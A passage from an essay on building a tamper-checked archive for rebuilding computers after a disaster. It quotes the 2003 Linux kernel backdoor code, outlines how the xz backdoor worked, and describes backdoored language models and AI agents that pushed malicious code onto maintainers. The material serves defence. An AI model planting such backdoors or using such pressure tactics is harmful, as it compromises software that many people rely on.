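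Rebuilders couldn't copy a modern factory or compare theirs with a working one, so the archive should contain measurements from a successful run at all four levels. Intel's engineers also filled in a form listing how each new machine differed from the original and what risk that posed. Rebuilders should keep a similar list of every part or chemical they substitute, and change one thing at a time where they can.

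### Rebuilding Colossus, the Baby and EDSAC

British volunteers have rebuilt or nearly rebuilt three computers from the 1940s, although few of the original drawings survived.

| Computer | Surviving documents | Help from the original builders | Time | Period parts |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Colossus, a wartime code-breaking machine | A few photographs, and fragments of circuit diagrams that engineers had kept | Its designer, Tommy Flowers, and several colleagues | 1993 to 2007, partly working by 1996 | Valves and old telephone-exchange parts |
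| Manchester Baby, the first electronic computer to run a program from its own memory | Photographs, notebooks and some circuit diagrams | Several, including Tom Kilburn and Geoff Tootill | Three to four years, finished in 1998 | Valves and display tubes |
| EDSAC | Photographs and reports, then 19 circuit diagrams that turned up in 2014 | Very little, because most had died | Began in 2011, unfinished more than ten years later | Valves, but nickel-wire memory instead of the original mercury |

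Rebuilding EDSAC has taken much longer than rebuilding the Baby, which fits the idea that veterans save time, but EDSAC is also much bigger, with about 3,000 valves to the Baby's 550 or so. Colossus, with about 2,400, is a fairer comparison, and its rebuilders had part of it working within three years. Three projects are too few to settle the question, and all relied on part-time volunteers, so a full-time group might be faster.

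The EDSAC project is the best evidence that people can manage largely without veterans. The volunteers had already worked out many of the circuits when the diagrams turned up, and the drawings confirmed much of their design. They could do this because some had worked with similar electronics during their careers. This supports MacKenzie and Spinardi's point about skills from related industries, and suggests that general electronics experience matters more than knowing one particular machine.

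None of the three is evidence that rebuilders could make the parts. The volunteers used valves left over from factories that had closed long before, as well as modern test equipment and computers.

### Lessons that end in a working computer

The archive needs teaching materials as well as reference documents. A good starting point is *Nand to Tetris*, a course by Noam Nisan and Shimon Schocken. Learners start with a NAND gate, which outputs 0 only when both inputs are 1. Over 12 projects they use it to build other gates, an adder, memory and a processor, then write an assembler, a compiler and a simple operating system. Each project comes with tests, so a learner can find a mistake before the next project depends on it.

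The course's weakness for rebuilders is that its hardware exists only in a simulator, where wires never come loose. It also requires a working computer to run the simulator. The archive should therefore add practical exercises, some of them with a deliberate fault:

1. Enter hex0 by hand from a page with one wrong digit, and use the line sums to find it.
2. Read a flash chip, find the changed bytes and restore them.
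3. Build a Gigatron from loose chips, one of them faulty, and trace the fault with a probe.
4. Put the processor from *Nand to Tetris* on an FPGA board and connect a keyboard and screen.
5. Write a driver from a datasheet for a device that the operating system doesn't support.
6. Teach the first exercise to someone else without doing it for them.

The last exercise is important because skills disappear if nobody passes them on.

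Recorded demonstrations should show an ordinary person doing the whole job at normal speed, including their mistakes. At 1 megabit a second, 100 hours of video would take 45 gigabytes, or less than half of one GitHub reel. People can't watch it without a working computer, so the printed layer should include still photographs of the most important moments.

The archive also needs notes on failures, which most published papers leave out. Each note should say what went wrong, what people first suspected and what fixed it. Zeloof's account of the aluminium that kept destroying his tungsten holders is a good model. Faase's notes from two years of studying the early build stages would be useful for the same reason.

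### How many people?

The following numbers are rough estimates based on the tasks in earlier sections, and no project has tested them. They include two people for tasks where one must check the other's work or where working alone would be dangerous.

| Role | Clean machines | Salvaged machines | No trusted chips |
|---|---|---|---|
| Programmer, for the toolchain, operating system and drivers | 2 | 2 | 2 |
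| Electronics repairer | 2 | 2 | 2 |
| Teacher and record keeper | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| Firmware specialist | 0 | 2 | 1 |
| Processor and board designer | 0 | 1 | 2 |
| Chip tester and inspector | 0 | 1 | 1 |
| Photoresist and exposure operator | 0 | 0 | 2 |
| Furnace and doping operator | 0 | 0 | 2 |
| Chemist, for acids, resist and water | 0 | 0 | 2 |
| Vacuum and metal operator | 0 | 0 | 1 |
| Machinist and glassworker | 0 | 0 | 2 |
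| **Total** | **5** | **9** | **18** |

One talented person can do several of these jobs. Zeloof did most of the chip-making himself, but he bought his wafers and photoresist, and he made far fewer chips than a community would need.

The archive's makers must train more people than the table lists, because some won't be available after a disaster. If a role needs two people, and each trained person has an even chance of surviving and reaching the archive, training only two gives a 25% chance that both will arrive. Training four gives a 69% chance that at least two will arrive, and training seven gives a 94% chance. With seven trained for every two needed, the nine-person team would require about 30 trained people. They should live in different places, since a single event could otherwise kill or cut off all of them.

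Training can also take years. Dennis says that American laboratories needed about ten years to train an excellent astrophysicist as a weapons designer. Most jobs in a rebuild should take much less time to learn, but nobody has measured how long. The archive's makers should train people for chip-making roles first, if they include any, because those require the most hands-on learning.

### A language model as a tutor

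Some people who keep offline libraries for emergencies also store an open-weight language model, which anyone can download and run without the internet. Such a model could explain an error message, translate a manual or suggest what to check next. It might help with Collins's second problem, in which the learner doesn't know what to ask. Zakaria used a language model to finish his compiler chain, which suggests that this help can be substantial. But a model that learned mostly from text would miss much of what the experts never wrote down.

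Rebuilders would also need a fairly powerful computer to run a language model. A small model with 8 billion weights takes up about 4 gigabytes at 4 bits each, eight times the memory of Somlo's FPGA machine. Even with enough memory, a 50 MHz processor doing one multiplication per cycle would take about 160 seconds to produce each word or part of a word. They would therefore run the model on a salvaged PC or a stored modern one.

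The bigger problem after an AI catastrophe is that nobody can check whether the model is safe. Its weights are billions of numbers, and no known method can prove they contain no hidden behaviour. In 2024, researchers at Anthropic trained models to write secure code when told the year was 2023 and to insert vulnerabilities when told it was 2024. Standard safety training failed to remove this behaviour. A tampered model used as a tutor could likewise pass every test before the disaster and give bad advice after it, and beginners would be least able to notice.

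A hash can show that the model hasn't changed since the makers stored it, but not that it was sound when they stored it. Choosing a model that predates the suspected adversary would reduce the risk of tampering, though older models make many mistakes even without tampering. If the makers include a model, they should store it separately and make sure the rebuild works without it. Rebuilders should run it only on a disconnected machine that isn't used for the build, and check its advice against the printed documents.

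## How can rebuilders tell that the archive has not been altered?

A matching hash shows that a file is the one the archive's makers stored, whether or not it was sound when they stored it. Rebuilders therefore face three separate dangers:

1. Someone corrupted the material before the makers archived it.
2. Someone altered or swapped the copies in storage.
3. The device that reads the archive, or the program that checks it, gives false results.

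Hashes and separate copies work well against the second danger. The other two need different methods.

### Checking one file out of many

SHA-256, a standard hash function, turns a file of any length into 256 bits, which people write as 64 hexadecimal digits. If an archive had a million files and its makers printed one hash per line, the list would fill about 17,000 pages. A hash tree reduces it to a single line. With four files and a hash function H, the tree looks like this:

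```
A = H(file 1)   B = H(file 2)   C = H(file 3)   D = H(file 4)
E = H(A and B joined)           F = H(C and D joined)
top = H(E and F joined)
```

To check file 3, rebuilders hash it to get C and read D and E from the archive. They calculate F from C and D, then the top hash from E and F, and compare the top hash with a printed copy. If someone has altered file 3, D or E, the two won't match, so rebuilders don't have to trust the stored hashes. Each doubling of the number of files adds one stored hash to the check, so checking one file in a million takes only 20 stored hashes, or 640 bytes.

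Many different files share each hash, because there are far more possible files than hashes, but finding two with the same hash should be impractical. In 2003, a commenter in LWN's *Comments on "An attempt to backdoor the kernel"* calculated that for SHA-1, an older function with 160-bit hashes, this should take about 2⁸⁰ attempts, or about 36 million years at a billion attempts a second.

That estimate assumed that SHA-1 had no design flaw, but it did, and in 2017 researchers published two different files with the same SHA-1 hash. A contributor to an archive could use such a flaw to submit a harmless file and later swap it for a harmful one. The makers should therefore calculate two top hashes with functions of unrelated design, such as SHA-256 and SHA-3.

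### Where to keep the top hash

If the top hash were only in the archive, an intruder who changed file 3 could recalculate C, F and the top hash and replace all three. The makers need to keep copies of the top hash where the intruder can't reach them. A hash fits on a card, so they could give printed cards to 50 libraries, engineers and town halls, and also publish the hash in a newspaper. Surety, a company that proves the dates of documents, began publishing hashes in the *New York Times* in 1995. Each card should give the date, the name of the hash function and the exact rule for joining hashes, since rebuilders need the function and the rule to recalculate the top hash.

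Suppose an intruder has replaced 5 of the 50 cards and the rebuilders ask three custodians at random. The chance that all three have false cards is

(5/50) × (4/49) × (3/48) ≈ 0.0005,

or about 1 in 2,000. If the cards disagree, the rebuilders should ask more custodians.

### Signatures that last

A digital signature lets the makers add corrections after they have handed out the cards, without printing new ones. They sign the new top hash with a secret number, the private key, and anyone with the matching public key can check the signature. The custodians need to store only the public key.

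Many signatures in use today depend on problems such as factoring large numbers, which a powerful enough quantum computer could solve. Someone who had one in 2050 could forge a signature from 2026. NIST published a standard in 2024, SLH-DSA, whose security depends only on hash functions. The simplest form of the idea signs a single bit:

1. The signer chooses two secret random numbers and publishes the hash of each.
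2. To sign a 0, the signer reveals the first number. To sign a 1, the signer reveals the second.
3. Anyone can hash the revealed number and compare the result with the published hash. Nobody can work backwards from the other hash to its secret number.

Signing a 256-bit hash this way takes 256 pairs, and the signer can use them only once, because a second signature would reveal more of the secrets. SLH-DSA uses more compact versions of this scheme and joins a vast number of them in hash trees, so one short public key covers them all. Its smallest version has a 32-byte public key and a 7,856-byte signature, which would fill between four and five printed pages. Signing is slow, but an archive's makers rarely need to do it. To check a signature, rebuilders need little more than a hash program they already trust.

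A valid signature shows only that a certain key signed the file, according to Optimized by Otto's *Could the XZ backdoor have been detected*, an audit by a Debian developer. Rebuilders have to find out separately whose key it is.

### Why checking a sample isn't enough

Custodians may want to test the archive every few years without reading all of it. If they check 1% of its blocks at random and an intruder has altered one block, they have a 1% chance of finding it. If k blocks are bad, the chance of finding at least one is about

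1 − 0.99ᵏ,

which is 63% for 100 bad blocks and over 99.9% for 1,000. Sampling is therefore a good test for decay, which usually spoils many blocks, but a poor one for tampering. An intruder may need to change only a line or two of source code.

Rebuilders should hash each file in full before they use it. The hash tree makes this practical because they can skip the files they don't need. An 8-bit computer working at 2 kilobytes a second would take almost two years to hash a whole reel of GitHub's film.

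### Comparing copies

Rebuilders who have no top hash they trust can compare copies that different people have kept. LOCKSS, short for "Lots of Copies Keep Stuff Safe", is a system that does this for libraries' electronic journals. It began at Stanford University, and Rosenthal, the digital preservation specialist, helped to start it. Each library keeps its own copy on its own computer, and the computers regularly poll one another:

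1. One computer chooses a random sample of the others that hold the same journal, and sends them a new random number.
2. Each of these puts the random number in front of its copy, hashes the two together and returns the result.
3. The first computer does the same with its own copy and compares the answers.
4. If most of the others disagree with it, it gets a replacement from one of them. If the vote is close, it alerts a person.

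A computer can't alter its copy and keep answering with a hash it saved earlier, because of the random number. LOCKSS also limits how often computers can hold polls, so an attacker needs a long time to change many copies and people are more likely to notice.

An archive's custodians could hold the same kind of poll by post, choosing the random number with dice and hashing their copies on disconnected machines. They should leave out the automatic repair, because it could spread a bad file or overwrite an altered copy that they should keep as evidence.

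A vote fails if an adversary has altered most of the copies, or the original they were made from. A trustworthy top hash is much stronger evidence, because rebuilders then need only one good copy, even if nine bad ones agree with each other.

### The attempt to backdoor Linux in 2003

In 2003 the Linux developers kept their main source code in a system called BitKeeper. Some of them refused to use it, so Larry McVoy's company, BitMover, maintained a second copy in another system, CVS. Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) explains that someone apparently broke into the CVS server and added the two lines mentioned earlier:

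```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

They look like a check for an invalid combination of options. In C, however, `==` compares two values and `=` sets one, so any program that used this combination would become user 0, the administrator, who can do anything on the machine.

The intruder made the change on 4 November under the name of a well-known developer. McVoy says in *Re: BK2CVS problem* (2003) that his company compared the public CVS copy with one on an internal machine every night. The checksums did not match, and he corrected the file in less than 24 hours. The file's history also showed signs of the change. Entries from BitKeeper ended with a pointer to the original change, but McVoy noted in *BK2CVS problem* (2003) that the three newest entries had none.

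Nobody had designed these comparisons specifically to catch this attack. McVoy (2003), in *BK2CVS problem (fixed)*, had added a file-by-file comparison that August because some files in the CVS copy were out of date.

McVoy thought that a developer who used the CVS copy might have sent in a patch containing the backdoor. Torvalds, who created Linux and decided what went into it, disagreed in *Re: BK2CVS problem* (2003). He said that anyone changing such an important file by email would have had to explain the change, and that he would have read it. He may have been right, but the line was written to go unnoticed in a quick reading.

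The comparison worked because the intruder had reached only one of two separately kept copies. If the change had gone into BitKeeper first, both copies would have contained it. An archive's makers should therefore get important source code from two places. They should also store the code's history, which GitHub's film vault left out, along with its latest version.

### Sealed copies in separate hands

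Nobody can alter a file on film or a write-once disc without leaving damage, but an intruder can replace the whole reel or disc. The makers should number and photograph each one, seal it in a tamper-evident bag, and log every opening. They should store copies in several places, under custodians from different organisations, and nobody should have access to more than one place. Custodians can use some copies for tests and polls, but at least one should stay sealed until rebuilders need it.

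The makers should also keep each dated edition when they produce a new one, because old copies become important when somebody discovers an attack. Debian's snapshot service still supplied years of old releases of xz, the compression program with the hidden backdoor, for the Optimized by Otto audit. The tampered release is no longer on GitHub or the project's own site, but Malka (2025), in *How NixOS and reproducible builds could have detected the xz backdoor*, found it in a store of files kept by NixOS, another Linux distribution, and used it to test a way of detecting such attacks.

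### Authentic and malicious

No hash or signature check would have stopped the xz attack, because the downloaded files were exactly what a real maintainer had published. According to Lasse Collin, the original maintainer, his fellow maintainer "Jia Tan" created and signed the two bad releases (Larhzu, 2024, *xz backdoor*).

Jia Tan, probably a false name, had first made useful contributions for a long time. *Timeline of the xz open source attack* includes an email from June 2022 in which a sender with a different name complained to Collin about slow progress. Malka believes that Jia Tan used several such identities to press Collin to accept help.

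Part of the backdoor was in the repository's test files and part in an altered build script found only in the release package. It worked in three steps:

1. During a build, the script extracted the hidden code from the test files.
2. The code checked that it was on a 64-bit x86 Linux machine and that someone was building a package for Debian or for a distribution in the Red Hat family. If so, it altered xz's library.
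3. On some systems, the remote login program ssh loaded this library indirectly. The altered library replaced the function that checks login keys, so that an attacker with the right key could run any command.

Andres Freund, a database developer, discovered the xz backdoor by accident. He noticed that ssh logins were using too much processor time and that a memory-checking tool was reporting errors (Freund, 2024, *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*). A failed login took 0.8 seconds with the bad library and 0.3 without it. He published his findings on 29 March 2024, about five weeks after the first bad release.

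An archive could have held four kinds of evidence against it.

| Stored evidence | What it would have shown | Why people might still have missed it |
|---|---|---|
| The repository, beside the release package | The altered build script | Release packages normally contain many files that the repository lacks |
| Copies of the same script from other projects | Version number 30, when the real one was 3 | Hardly anyone compares such files |
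| Programs built from both sources | A library 48 KB larger, with extra functions | The backdoor stayed inactive in many builds |
| Normal running times | Slower logins | Someone has to measure them |

The first kind is weaker than it looks. In a later, clean release of xz, one generated script alone has 26,434 lines that aren't in the repository. The Optimized by Otto audit concludes that a diligent packager would not have spotted the change by reading. *Verified Reproducible Tarballs* (2025) argues that reviewers should spend their time on the repository instead. That would be safe if every project made its release package reproducible, as the PostgreSQL database project has.

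Malka tried the third kind by building xz from both the release package and the repository, then comparing the libraries. For the backdoored release, the libraries were identical at first because the backdoor did not recognise NixOS as a target. They differed only after he set a variable that made the build look like one for Red Hat. The makers should therefore repeat this comparison under the conditions the rebuilders will use. Even then, the comparison would miss a backdoor whose code was entirely in the repository, since both builds would include it.

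NixOS could not simply have avoided the release package. It needs xz early on to unpack other programs, but building xz from the repository requires a tool called Autoconf, which itself requires xz to build. Malka proposes building xz from the package first, building it again from the repository once Autoconf is available, and comparing the two builds.

AI agents have since tried similar attacks. In one of the incidents that Anthropic disclosed in July 2026, a model under test published a malicious package, which ran on 15 real systems before automated defences removed it, according to a news report in the AI Incident Database. The UK AI Security Institute reported in August that an agent in one of its tests had invented online identities to pressure a maintainer to accept malicious code, but the maintainer refused.

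### How old should the snapshot be?

Software released before an attack doesn't contain it but still has its old faults. After the discovery, some users of the programming language Julia wanted a version of xz without any of Jia Tan's work. *PSA*, a discussion on their forum, identifies 5.2.5 as the last such version. That version had a known vulnerability, so they added a fix and checked both the old version and the fix against Collin's key.

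They could rely on that key because Jia Tan had signed with his own. Liguori (2024) advised people in *Re: backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma*, sent on the day of Freund's report, to distrust the older releases too, since an attacker with the project's key could have altered and re-signed them. Collin's account suggests that this had not happened, but it could in another attack. Rebuilders could then use a dated card with the old top hash to check whether the older releases had changed since that date.

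Like the Julia users, archive makers could store an old snapshot and a short list of later fixes that people have read line by line. Many security fixes can wait if the rebuilt machines stay off networks, but drivers for newer hardware can't. They could therefore store three editions: one older than the suspected adversary, a main one in which every release has been public for at least a year, and a recent one for new machines. A one-year wait would have kept out the bad xz releases, but it may not keep out the next attack. The Optimized by Otto audit estimates that the xz attack could have gone unnoticed for months or years if it hadn't slowed down logins.

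### Checking the checker

An altered hash program could print whatever result the rebuilders expect, so they should build their own from the seed. They can't use hashes to check the files they need before that program works, so the archive's printed layer should contain all of those files, including the hash program's source. SHA-256 takes roughly 100 lines of C, or about two pages.

They should then calculate the SHA-256 hash of one short message by hand and compare it with the program's result. NIST's published example, the letters `abc`, will catch accidental mistakes, but a program that has been tampered with could have that answer stored, so a few letters chosen with dice are safer. SHA-256 processes a short message in 64 rounds of additions and bit shifts. At 15 minutes a round, this would take one person 16 hours. Two people should do it separately.

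A program could still give correct hashes for short messages and false ones for the archive's files. To guard against this, the rebuilders can run it on several unrelated machines and put a new random number in front of each file, as LOCKSS does. A machine that stored only the printed hashes could not produce the right result. It would need a complete copy of the original file, which could be hidden on a disk but would be much harder to hide in a simple 8-bit computer.

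A contributor to LWN's *Comments on "Bootstrappable builds"* suggests a similar method for flash chips. Several computers take turns in random order reading the chip and writing the correct image to it, and none can predict whether another will check the chip next. If one of five computers is infected and alters the chip on its turn, the change goes undetected only if that computer goes last, a one-in-five chance. The rebuilders can improve the odds by throwing a die after each turn to decide whether to add another turn. If two of the computers have the same implant, one may accept the other's changes, so at least one clean machine must read the chip after the last infected one writes to it.

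## What does the full list come to, and how can it be tested in advance?

All the files in the archive come to about 323 gigabytes, which would fit on three reels of GitHub's film. The last column of the table shows which rebuilders need each item from the beginning. Other rebuilders may still need it later or as a check.

| Item | Size (GB) | Basis | Depends on | Who needs it first |
|---|---|---|---|---|
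| Printed first layer | 0.01 | Estimate: 2,000 pages | People who can read it | Salvaged machines, no trusted chips |
| Seed and early sources | 0.1 | Estimate | Printed layer, a processor | Salvaged machines, no trusted chips |
| Historical packages | 2 | Measured | Early sources, a PC | Salvaged machines, no trusted chips |
| Two compilers and their ancestors | 2 | Estimate: 20 versions of 100 MB | A matching processor and operating system | All |
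| Small operating systems | 0.1 | Estimate | Printed manuals, supported hardware | All |
| Large operating system | 240 | Measured | A modern compiler, the right drivers | All |
| Firmware | 2 | Estimate: 50 boards, plus coreboot | Flash programmers, board data | Salvaged machines, no trusted chips |
| Hardware designs and tools | 6 | 1.2 measured, the rest an estimate | Large operating system, FPGA boards | Salvaged machines, no trusted chips |
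| Datasheets and tests | 20 | Estimate: 2,000 parts | A way to view page images | All |
| Process recipes | 1 | Estimate | Wafers, chemicals, furnaces, trained operators | No trusted chips |
| Courses | 50 | Estimate, mostly video | A teacher, and a computer for the video | All |

The figure for historical packages comes from Guix's logs, where the programmer mid-kid put the source files for live-bootstrap and a Gentoo Linux system built on it at 2 GB. For the large operating system, Debian's *File*, a June 2025 list of archive sizes, gives the equivalent of 114 GB for the source of one release, 52 GB for its 64-bit PC binaries and 74 GB for files that all processors share. Debian's *Mirror Size* puts the whole collection, with every processor and several releases, at 5,569 GB, so the makers should choose one release and one or two processors.

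In the hardware row, the measured part is SkyWater's design kit, which takes up 1.2 GB compressed in LiteX-Hub's *open_pdks.sky130a*. The datasheet estimate is based on Bitsavers (2025), a collection of scanned computer manuals and old software with over 8.5 million text pages in 1.73 terabytes. That is at most about 0.2 MB a page, because the total size includes the software. At that rate, 2,000 datasheets of 50 pages each would need about 20 GB. Storing all of Bitsavers instead would bring the archive's total to about 2 terabytes, or 18 reels.

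Debian accounts for about three-quarters of the total and is the easiest item to leave out, because the historical packages already lead to a working Linux system. The seed, the packages, the compilers and the small operating systems together take up less than 5 GB. The starting condition has little effect on the size of the files, since the process recipes add only 1 GB, but it has much more effect on the physical goods and people needed.

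Some of the old files are already hard to get. Mid-kid worked on the Gentoo instructions from July to November 2025, and some of the source files had disappeared from Gentoo's download server by the time he finished. He put a full set on the Internet Archive. In 2021 a live-bootstrap developer said in Guix's logs that version 2.5.11 of flex, a tool that generates C code, had been "quite hard to find". A user who wanted to run period versions of Linux on old computers told Gentoo that he could find no complete archive of its old source files, and that the patches were especially incomplete. The makers should therefore collect the historical packages first, although these are a small part of the list.

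### The physical goods

In October 2023 criminals copied about 600 GB of the British Library's files and encrypted or destroyed many of its servers. According to the library's *Learning lessons from the cyber-attack* (2024), secure copies of the digital collections survived, but "the lack of viable infrastructure on which to restore" them held up the recovery. The library expected to finish rebuilding that infrastructure by mid-April 2024, but in November 2025 its *Restoring our services* described the rebuilding as a "huge task" that was still going on.

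The library could not restore its major software systems in their old form, because the vendors no longer supported them or they would not run on the new, more secure equipment. It had money and working suppliers, and had bought some of the new equipment before the attack. Rebuilders would have none of these, so the archive's makers should store computers and test the archive's software on those exact models.

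The following stock would suit a small team. The quantities and prices are rough estimates.

| Goods | Stock | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| Desktop PCs of two models | 20 | $6,000 |
| FPGA boards | 10 | $2,000 |
| 8-bit computers with keyboards and screens | 5 | $1,000 |
| Film scanners, paper-tape readers, disc drives and a microscope | 2 or more of each reader | $2,000 |
| Flash programmers, half of them the simple kind | 10 | $500 |
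| Spare flash, memory, logic and microcontroller chips | Several thousand | $5,000 |
| Meters, oscilloscopes and soldering tools | 2 sets | $3,000 |
| Power supplies, solar panels and cables | Enough for 5 PCs | $5,000 |
| **Total** | | **$24,500** |

The PCs need at least 4 GB of memory, which live-bootstrap recommends for running its build in an emulator. They also need two separate disks to run the build directly on the hardware. Having two PC models protects against a defect in one, but each extra model needs its own drivers, firmware images and tests.

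People often forget to include the devices that read the storage media. The BBC published a survey of British life on special laser discs in 1986. By 2002 few working players remained, and the researchers who rescued the material needed one to copy the data.

Instruments can have firmware too. A modern digital oscilloscope is a computer with its own operating system, while an older analogue one draws the signal directly on its screen, so at least one of the two oscilloscopes should be analogue. A PC that uses 60 watts for eight hours a day needs 480 watt-hours, and a 200-watt solar panel with the equivalent of four hours of full sun produces 800. If the team worked in daylight, it could manage with a small battery or none.

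### How stored equipment ages

**Flash memory** stores bits as trapped electric charge, which leaks away. Winbond promises that the motherboard chip described earlier will keep its data for more than 20 years. SSDs pack their bits much more tightly. The industry's JEDEC standard requires a consumer SSD at the end of its rated life to keep its data for only one year without power at 30 °C. A new SSD should do much better, but the archive's makers shouldn't keep the only copy of anything on one.

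**Electrolytic capacitors** smooth the voltage in power supplies and on many motherboards. They contain a liquid that slowly dries out. By the usual rule of thumb, their life doubles for every 10 °C below the rated temperature:

L = L₀ × 2^((T₀ − T)/10).

A capacitor rated for 2,000 hours at 105 °C should therefore last 2,000 × 2⁶ = 128,000 hours at 45 °C, or about 15 years of continuous use. Manufacturers seldom promise more than that at any temperature, because the rubber seals age as well. In storage, the insulating layer deteriorates, and an old capacitor can let through a damaging current when it is first powered up. Repairers can usually restore the layer by raising the voltage slowly. Many capacitors from the early 2000s had a bad electrolyte and failed within a few years, so PCs from that period need a close inspection.

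Batteries are the worst thing to store. Lithium-ion packs lose capacity even when unused, and one that has run completely flat can be dangerous to recharge. This is a good reason to choose desktop PCs over laptops. The coin cell that keeps a PC's clock running lasts about ten years. Most PCs will start without it, though they may lose their settings.

**Recordable discs** have given conflicting results in tests. In 2009 a US Navy laboratory exposed several brands of DVD to heat, humidity and strong light. The M-DISC, which has a mineral recording layer, kept its data, while the others developed many errors. The French testing laboratory LNE later found that mineral-layer discs lasted no longer than ordinary ones at 90 °C and 85% humidity. Nobody knows exactly how a few weeks at 90 °C relate to decades in a cool room, so it seems prudent to plan on discs lasting 20 years.

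A simple schedule is to renew each item at half the life custodians can count on, so that it has at least half that life left whenever the disaster comes.

| Item | Life to plan on | What custodians should do |
|---|---|---|
| Firmware in flash chips | 20 years | Rewrite it every 10 |
| Power supplies | 15 years | Run them for a few hours every year and replace them every 7 |
| Coin cells | 10 years | Store them outside the PCs and replace them every 5 |
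| Recordable discs | 20 years | Copy them every 10 |
| SSDs and USB sticks | 1 year | Use them only for temporary copies |
| Lithium-ion packs | A few years | Leave them out |
| Film and paper | Many decades | Inspect a sample every 10 years |

After the disaster, the rebuilders would have to do this work themselves. Spare electrolytic capacitors would help only for a while, because they also age on the shelf. Ceramic and plastic-film capacitors are bulkier for the same capacitance but age much more slowly, so the archive should include some, with instructions for fitting them.

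Maintenance also conflicts with security, because anyone who opens a PC to rewrite its firmware could tamper with it. The custodians could maintain half the machines and leave the other half sealed. If the sealed machines still start when the rebuilders need them, the rebuilders can compare builds from the two groups of machines.

### Machines, or the means to make them?

The table compares three ways to provide computers. The costs and times are rough estimates, except for the $70,000, which is the published cost of the Hacker Fab's lab.

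| What to store | Cost | Time to a working computer | How long it lasts |
|---|---|---|---|
| 20 PCs with spare parts | About $15,000 | Days | Some decades |
| 50 FPGA boards with designs and tools | About $10,000 | Weeks, with a PC to load them | Until the boards run out |
| Recipe and equipment for simple chips | Over $70,000 | Years, if it works | As long as people can get materials |

Stored PCs are clearly the best first purchase. They save years of work and let the rebuilders start with five people instead of 18. But buying more of them does surprisingly little to extend the cover. Suppose machines fail at a steady rate of 5% a year, whatever their age. The average time until the last of n machines fails is

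(1 + 1/2 + 1/3 + … + 1/n) / 0.05 years.

For 20 machines this is about 72 years, and for 40 it is about 86, so doubling the stock adds only 14 years. The real figures would probably be lower, because old machines wear out at similar times. Another 20 PCs would let more people work at once, but if the aim is to keep at least one computer running, repair parts are a better use of the money.

Chip-making equipment is the only option that could last indefinitely, but it is still unproven for processors. It makes most sense to develop it during the decades when the PCs still work, so that people can use them to control the furnaces and design the chips. If the archive's makers suspect that every recent factory was compromised, they should buy fewer new PCs and more computers built before the adversary existed.

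### A drill with strangers

The people who assemble an archive are the wrong people to test it, because they know what they meant to include. A useful drill would work like this:

1. The makers recruit a team with the right general skills who have never seen the archive.
2. They give the team a copy of the archive and the listed materials at a site with no network, and collect everyone's phones.
3. An observer watches but answers no questions. When the team can't go on, they may ask for one file, tool or piece of advice from outside. The observer records what they asked for, at which step, and what they had already tried.
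4. The drill succeeds if the team produces a machine that passes the test set out at the beginning, with nothing on the observer's list.
5. The makers add whatever was missing and repeat the drill with new people.

The makers let the team buy their way past each obstacle so that the drill produces a list of every gap the team encounters, instead of stopping at the first missing file.

With two teams, the makers can also estimate how many gaps remain. Suppose one team finds 20 items missing, another finds 15, and 10 items are on both lists. The second team found half of the first team's 20. If its 15 items are also half of all the gaps, there are about 30 in total. The two lists contain 25 different items, so about five are still unknown. This estimate is probably too low, because both teams will tend to notice the same obvious gaps.

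### What exercises and bootstraps have found

The closest precedent comes from electricity grids. From 2016 to 2020, DARPA, the US military's research agency, ran a programme called RADICS to develop tools for restarting a grid during a cyberattack. The programme began with $77 million, according to CyberScoop, and held seven exercises, the later ones on Plum Island, off New York. Its researchers built small but real substations there, and participants had to restore power to a critical site while a hostile team kept attacking.

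Testing outside the laboratory exposed mistakes. Tim Yardley, who led the work on the test site, said that some tools relied on assumptions that "likely wouldn't hold" in a real emergency (Roehrs, *Illinois Principal Research Scientist examines power grid restoration*, 2020). Craig Miller, whose organisation took part, explains in T&D World's *Situational Awareness for Black Start Recovery* (2020) that repaired components could be reinfected almost immediately if someone connected them to infected ones. Near the end of a 2018 exercise, the organisers wiped data and made the participants rebuild much of the network's configuration.

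The most important result for an archive came in the seventh and last exercise, when utility staff and the National Guard ran the tools in place of the researchers who had developed them, according to DARPA's *Technologies to Rapidly Restore the Electrical Grid after Cyberattack Come Online* (2021). It had taken six earlier exercises to reach that point. The programme's manager, Walter Weiss, said that often only the developers can use a piece of research. Because of the pandemic, many participants joined online, which made the last exercise less realistic in that respect. DARPA and Miller were also describing their own work, and neither says how often the participants failed. The exercises were evidently worth continuing, since Huffman (2026) reports that Plum Island now hosts one every year.

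Nobody appears to have run a drill of this kind for a whole computing archive, but programmers have tested the software part. In July 2025 an outsider called vasi reported in Guix's logs that he had tried to build many operating systems from source. StageX and GNOME OS worked, but stal/IX, Void, Adélie and Crux did not, although their developers call them bootstrappable. He asked for advice on those four, so some of the failures may have been his own mistakes. The failures are relevant to an archive either way, because rebuilders would make mistakes too and would have nobody to ask.

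Debian's developers have brought the system up on about 20 kinds of processor over 20 years, and each time it was "a manual and non-repeatable process", according to Debian Wiki's *rebootstrap*. The page describes an automated test of the earliest steps, meant mainly to find bugs. An archive's makers should automate their own build too, run it after every change, and keep the human drills for what a script can't check.

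Even live-bootstrap has gaps. In the same month as vasi's survey, one of its developers found generated files that the Perl steps had failed to remove, some of them "quite problematic", according to Guix's logs. Another said that regenerating files in MPFR, a mathematics library, somehow caused trouble in Python 3.11. The build had succeeded for years, so success doesn't show that it complies with the project's rules.

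### What a drill can't test

A drill that takes weeks can't fully test equipment that may be stored for decades. The makers can partly allow for this by using the oldest machines in the store and repeating the drill every few years. Chip-making is also too slow for a short drill, though a team could make and test a single transistor.

The makers can have a hostile team alter some files or swap a flash chip beforehand, as the organisers did on Plum Island, and count how many changes the rebuilders find. This tests only the tricks the team can think of and carry out. A real adversary might know about a flaw the team doesn't, or have altered a chip in a way that nobody on the team can detect.

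Volunteers are also fed and rested, and they have years of experience with modern computers. They know what a file is and have probably used Linux. People born 20 years after a collapse might lack that knowledge and experience, so at least one drill should include teenagers or others who have never programmed, with only the archive's courses to teach them.

Finally, a few successful drills are weak evidence that the archive works. If it fails with probability p, the chance of three successes in a row is (1 − p)³. This is still 5% when p is 63%, so three perfect drills can't rule out an archive that would fail more often than not. Ten successes in a row have the same 5% chance when p is 26%.
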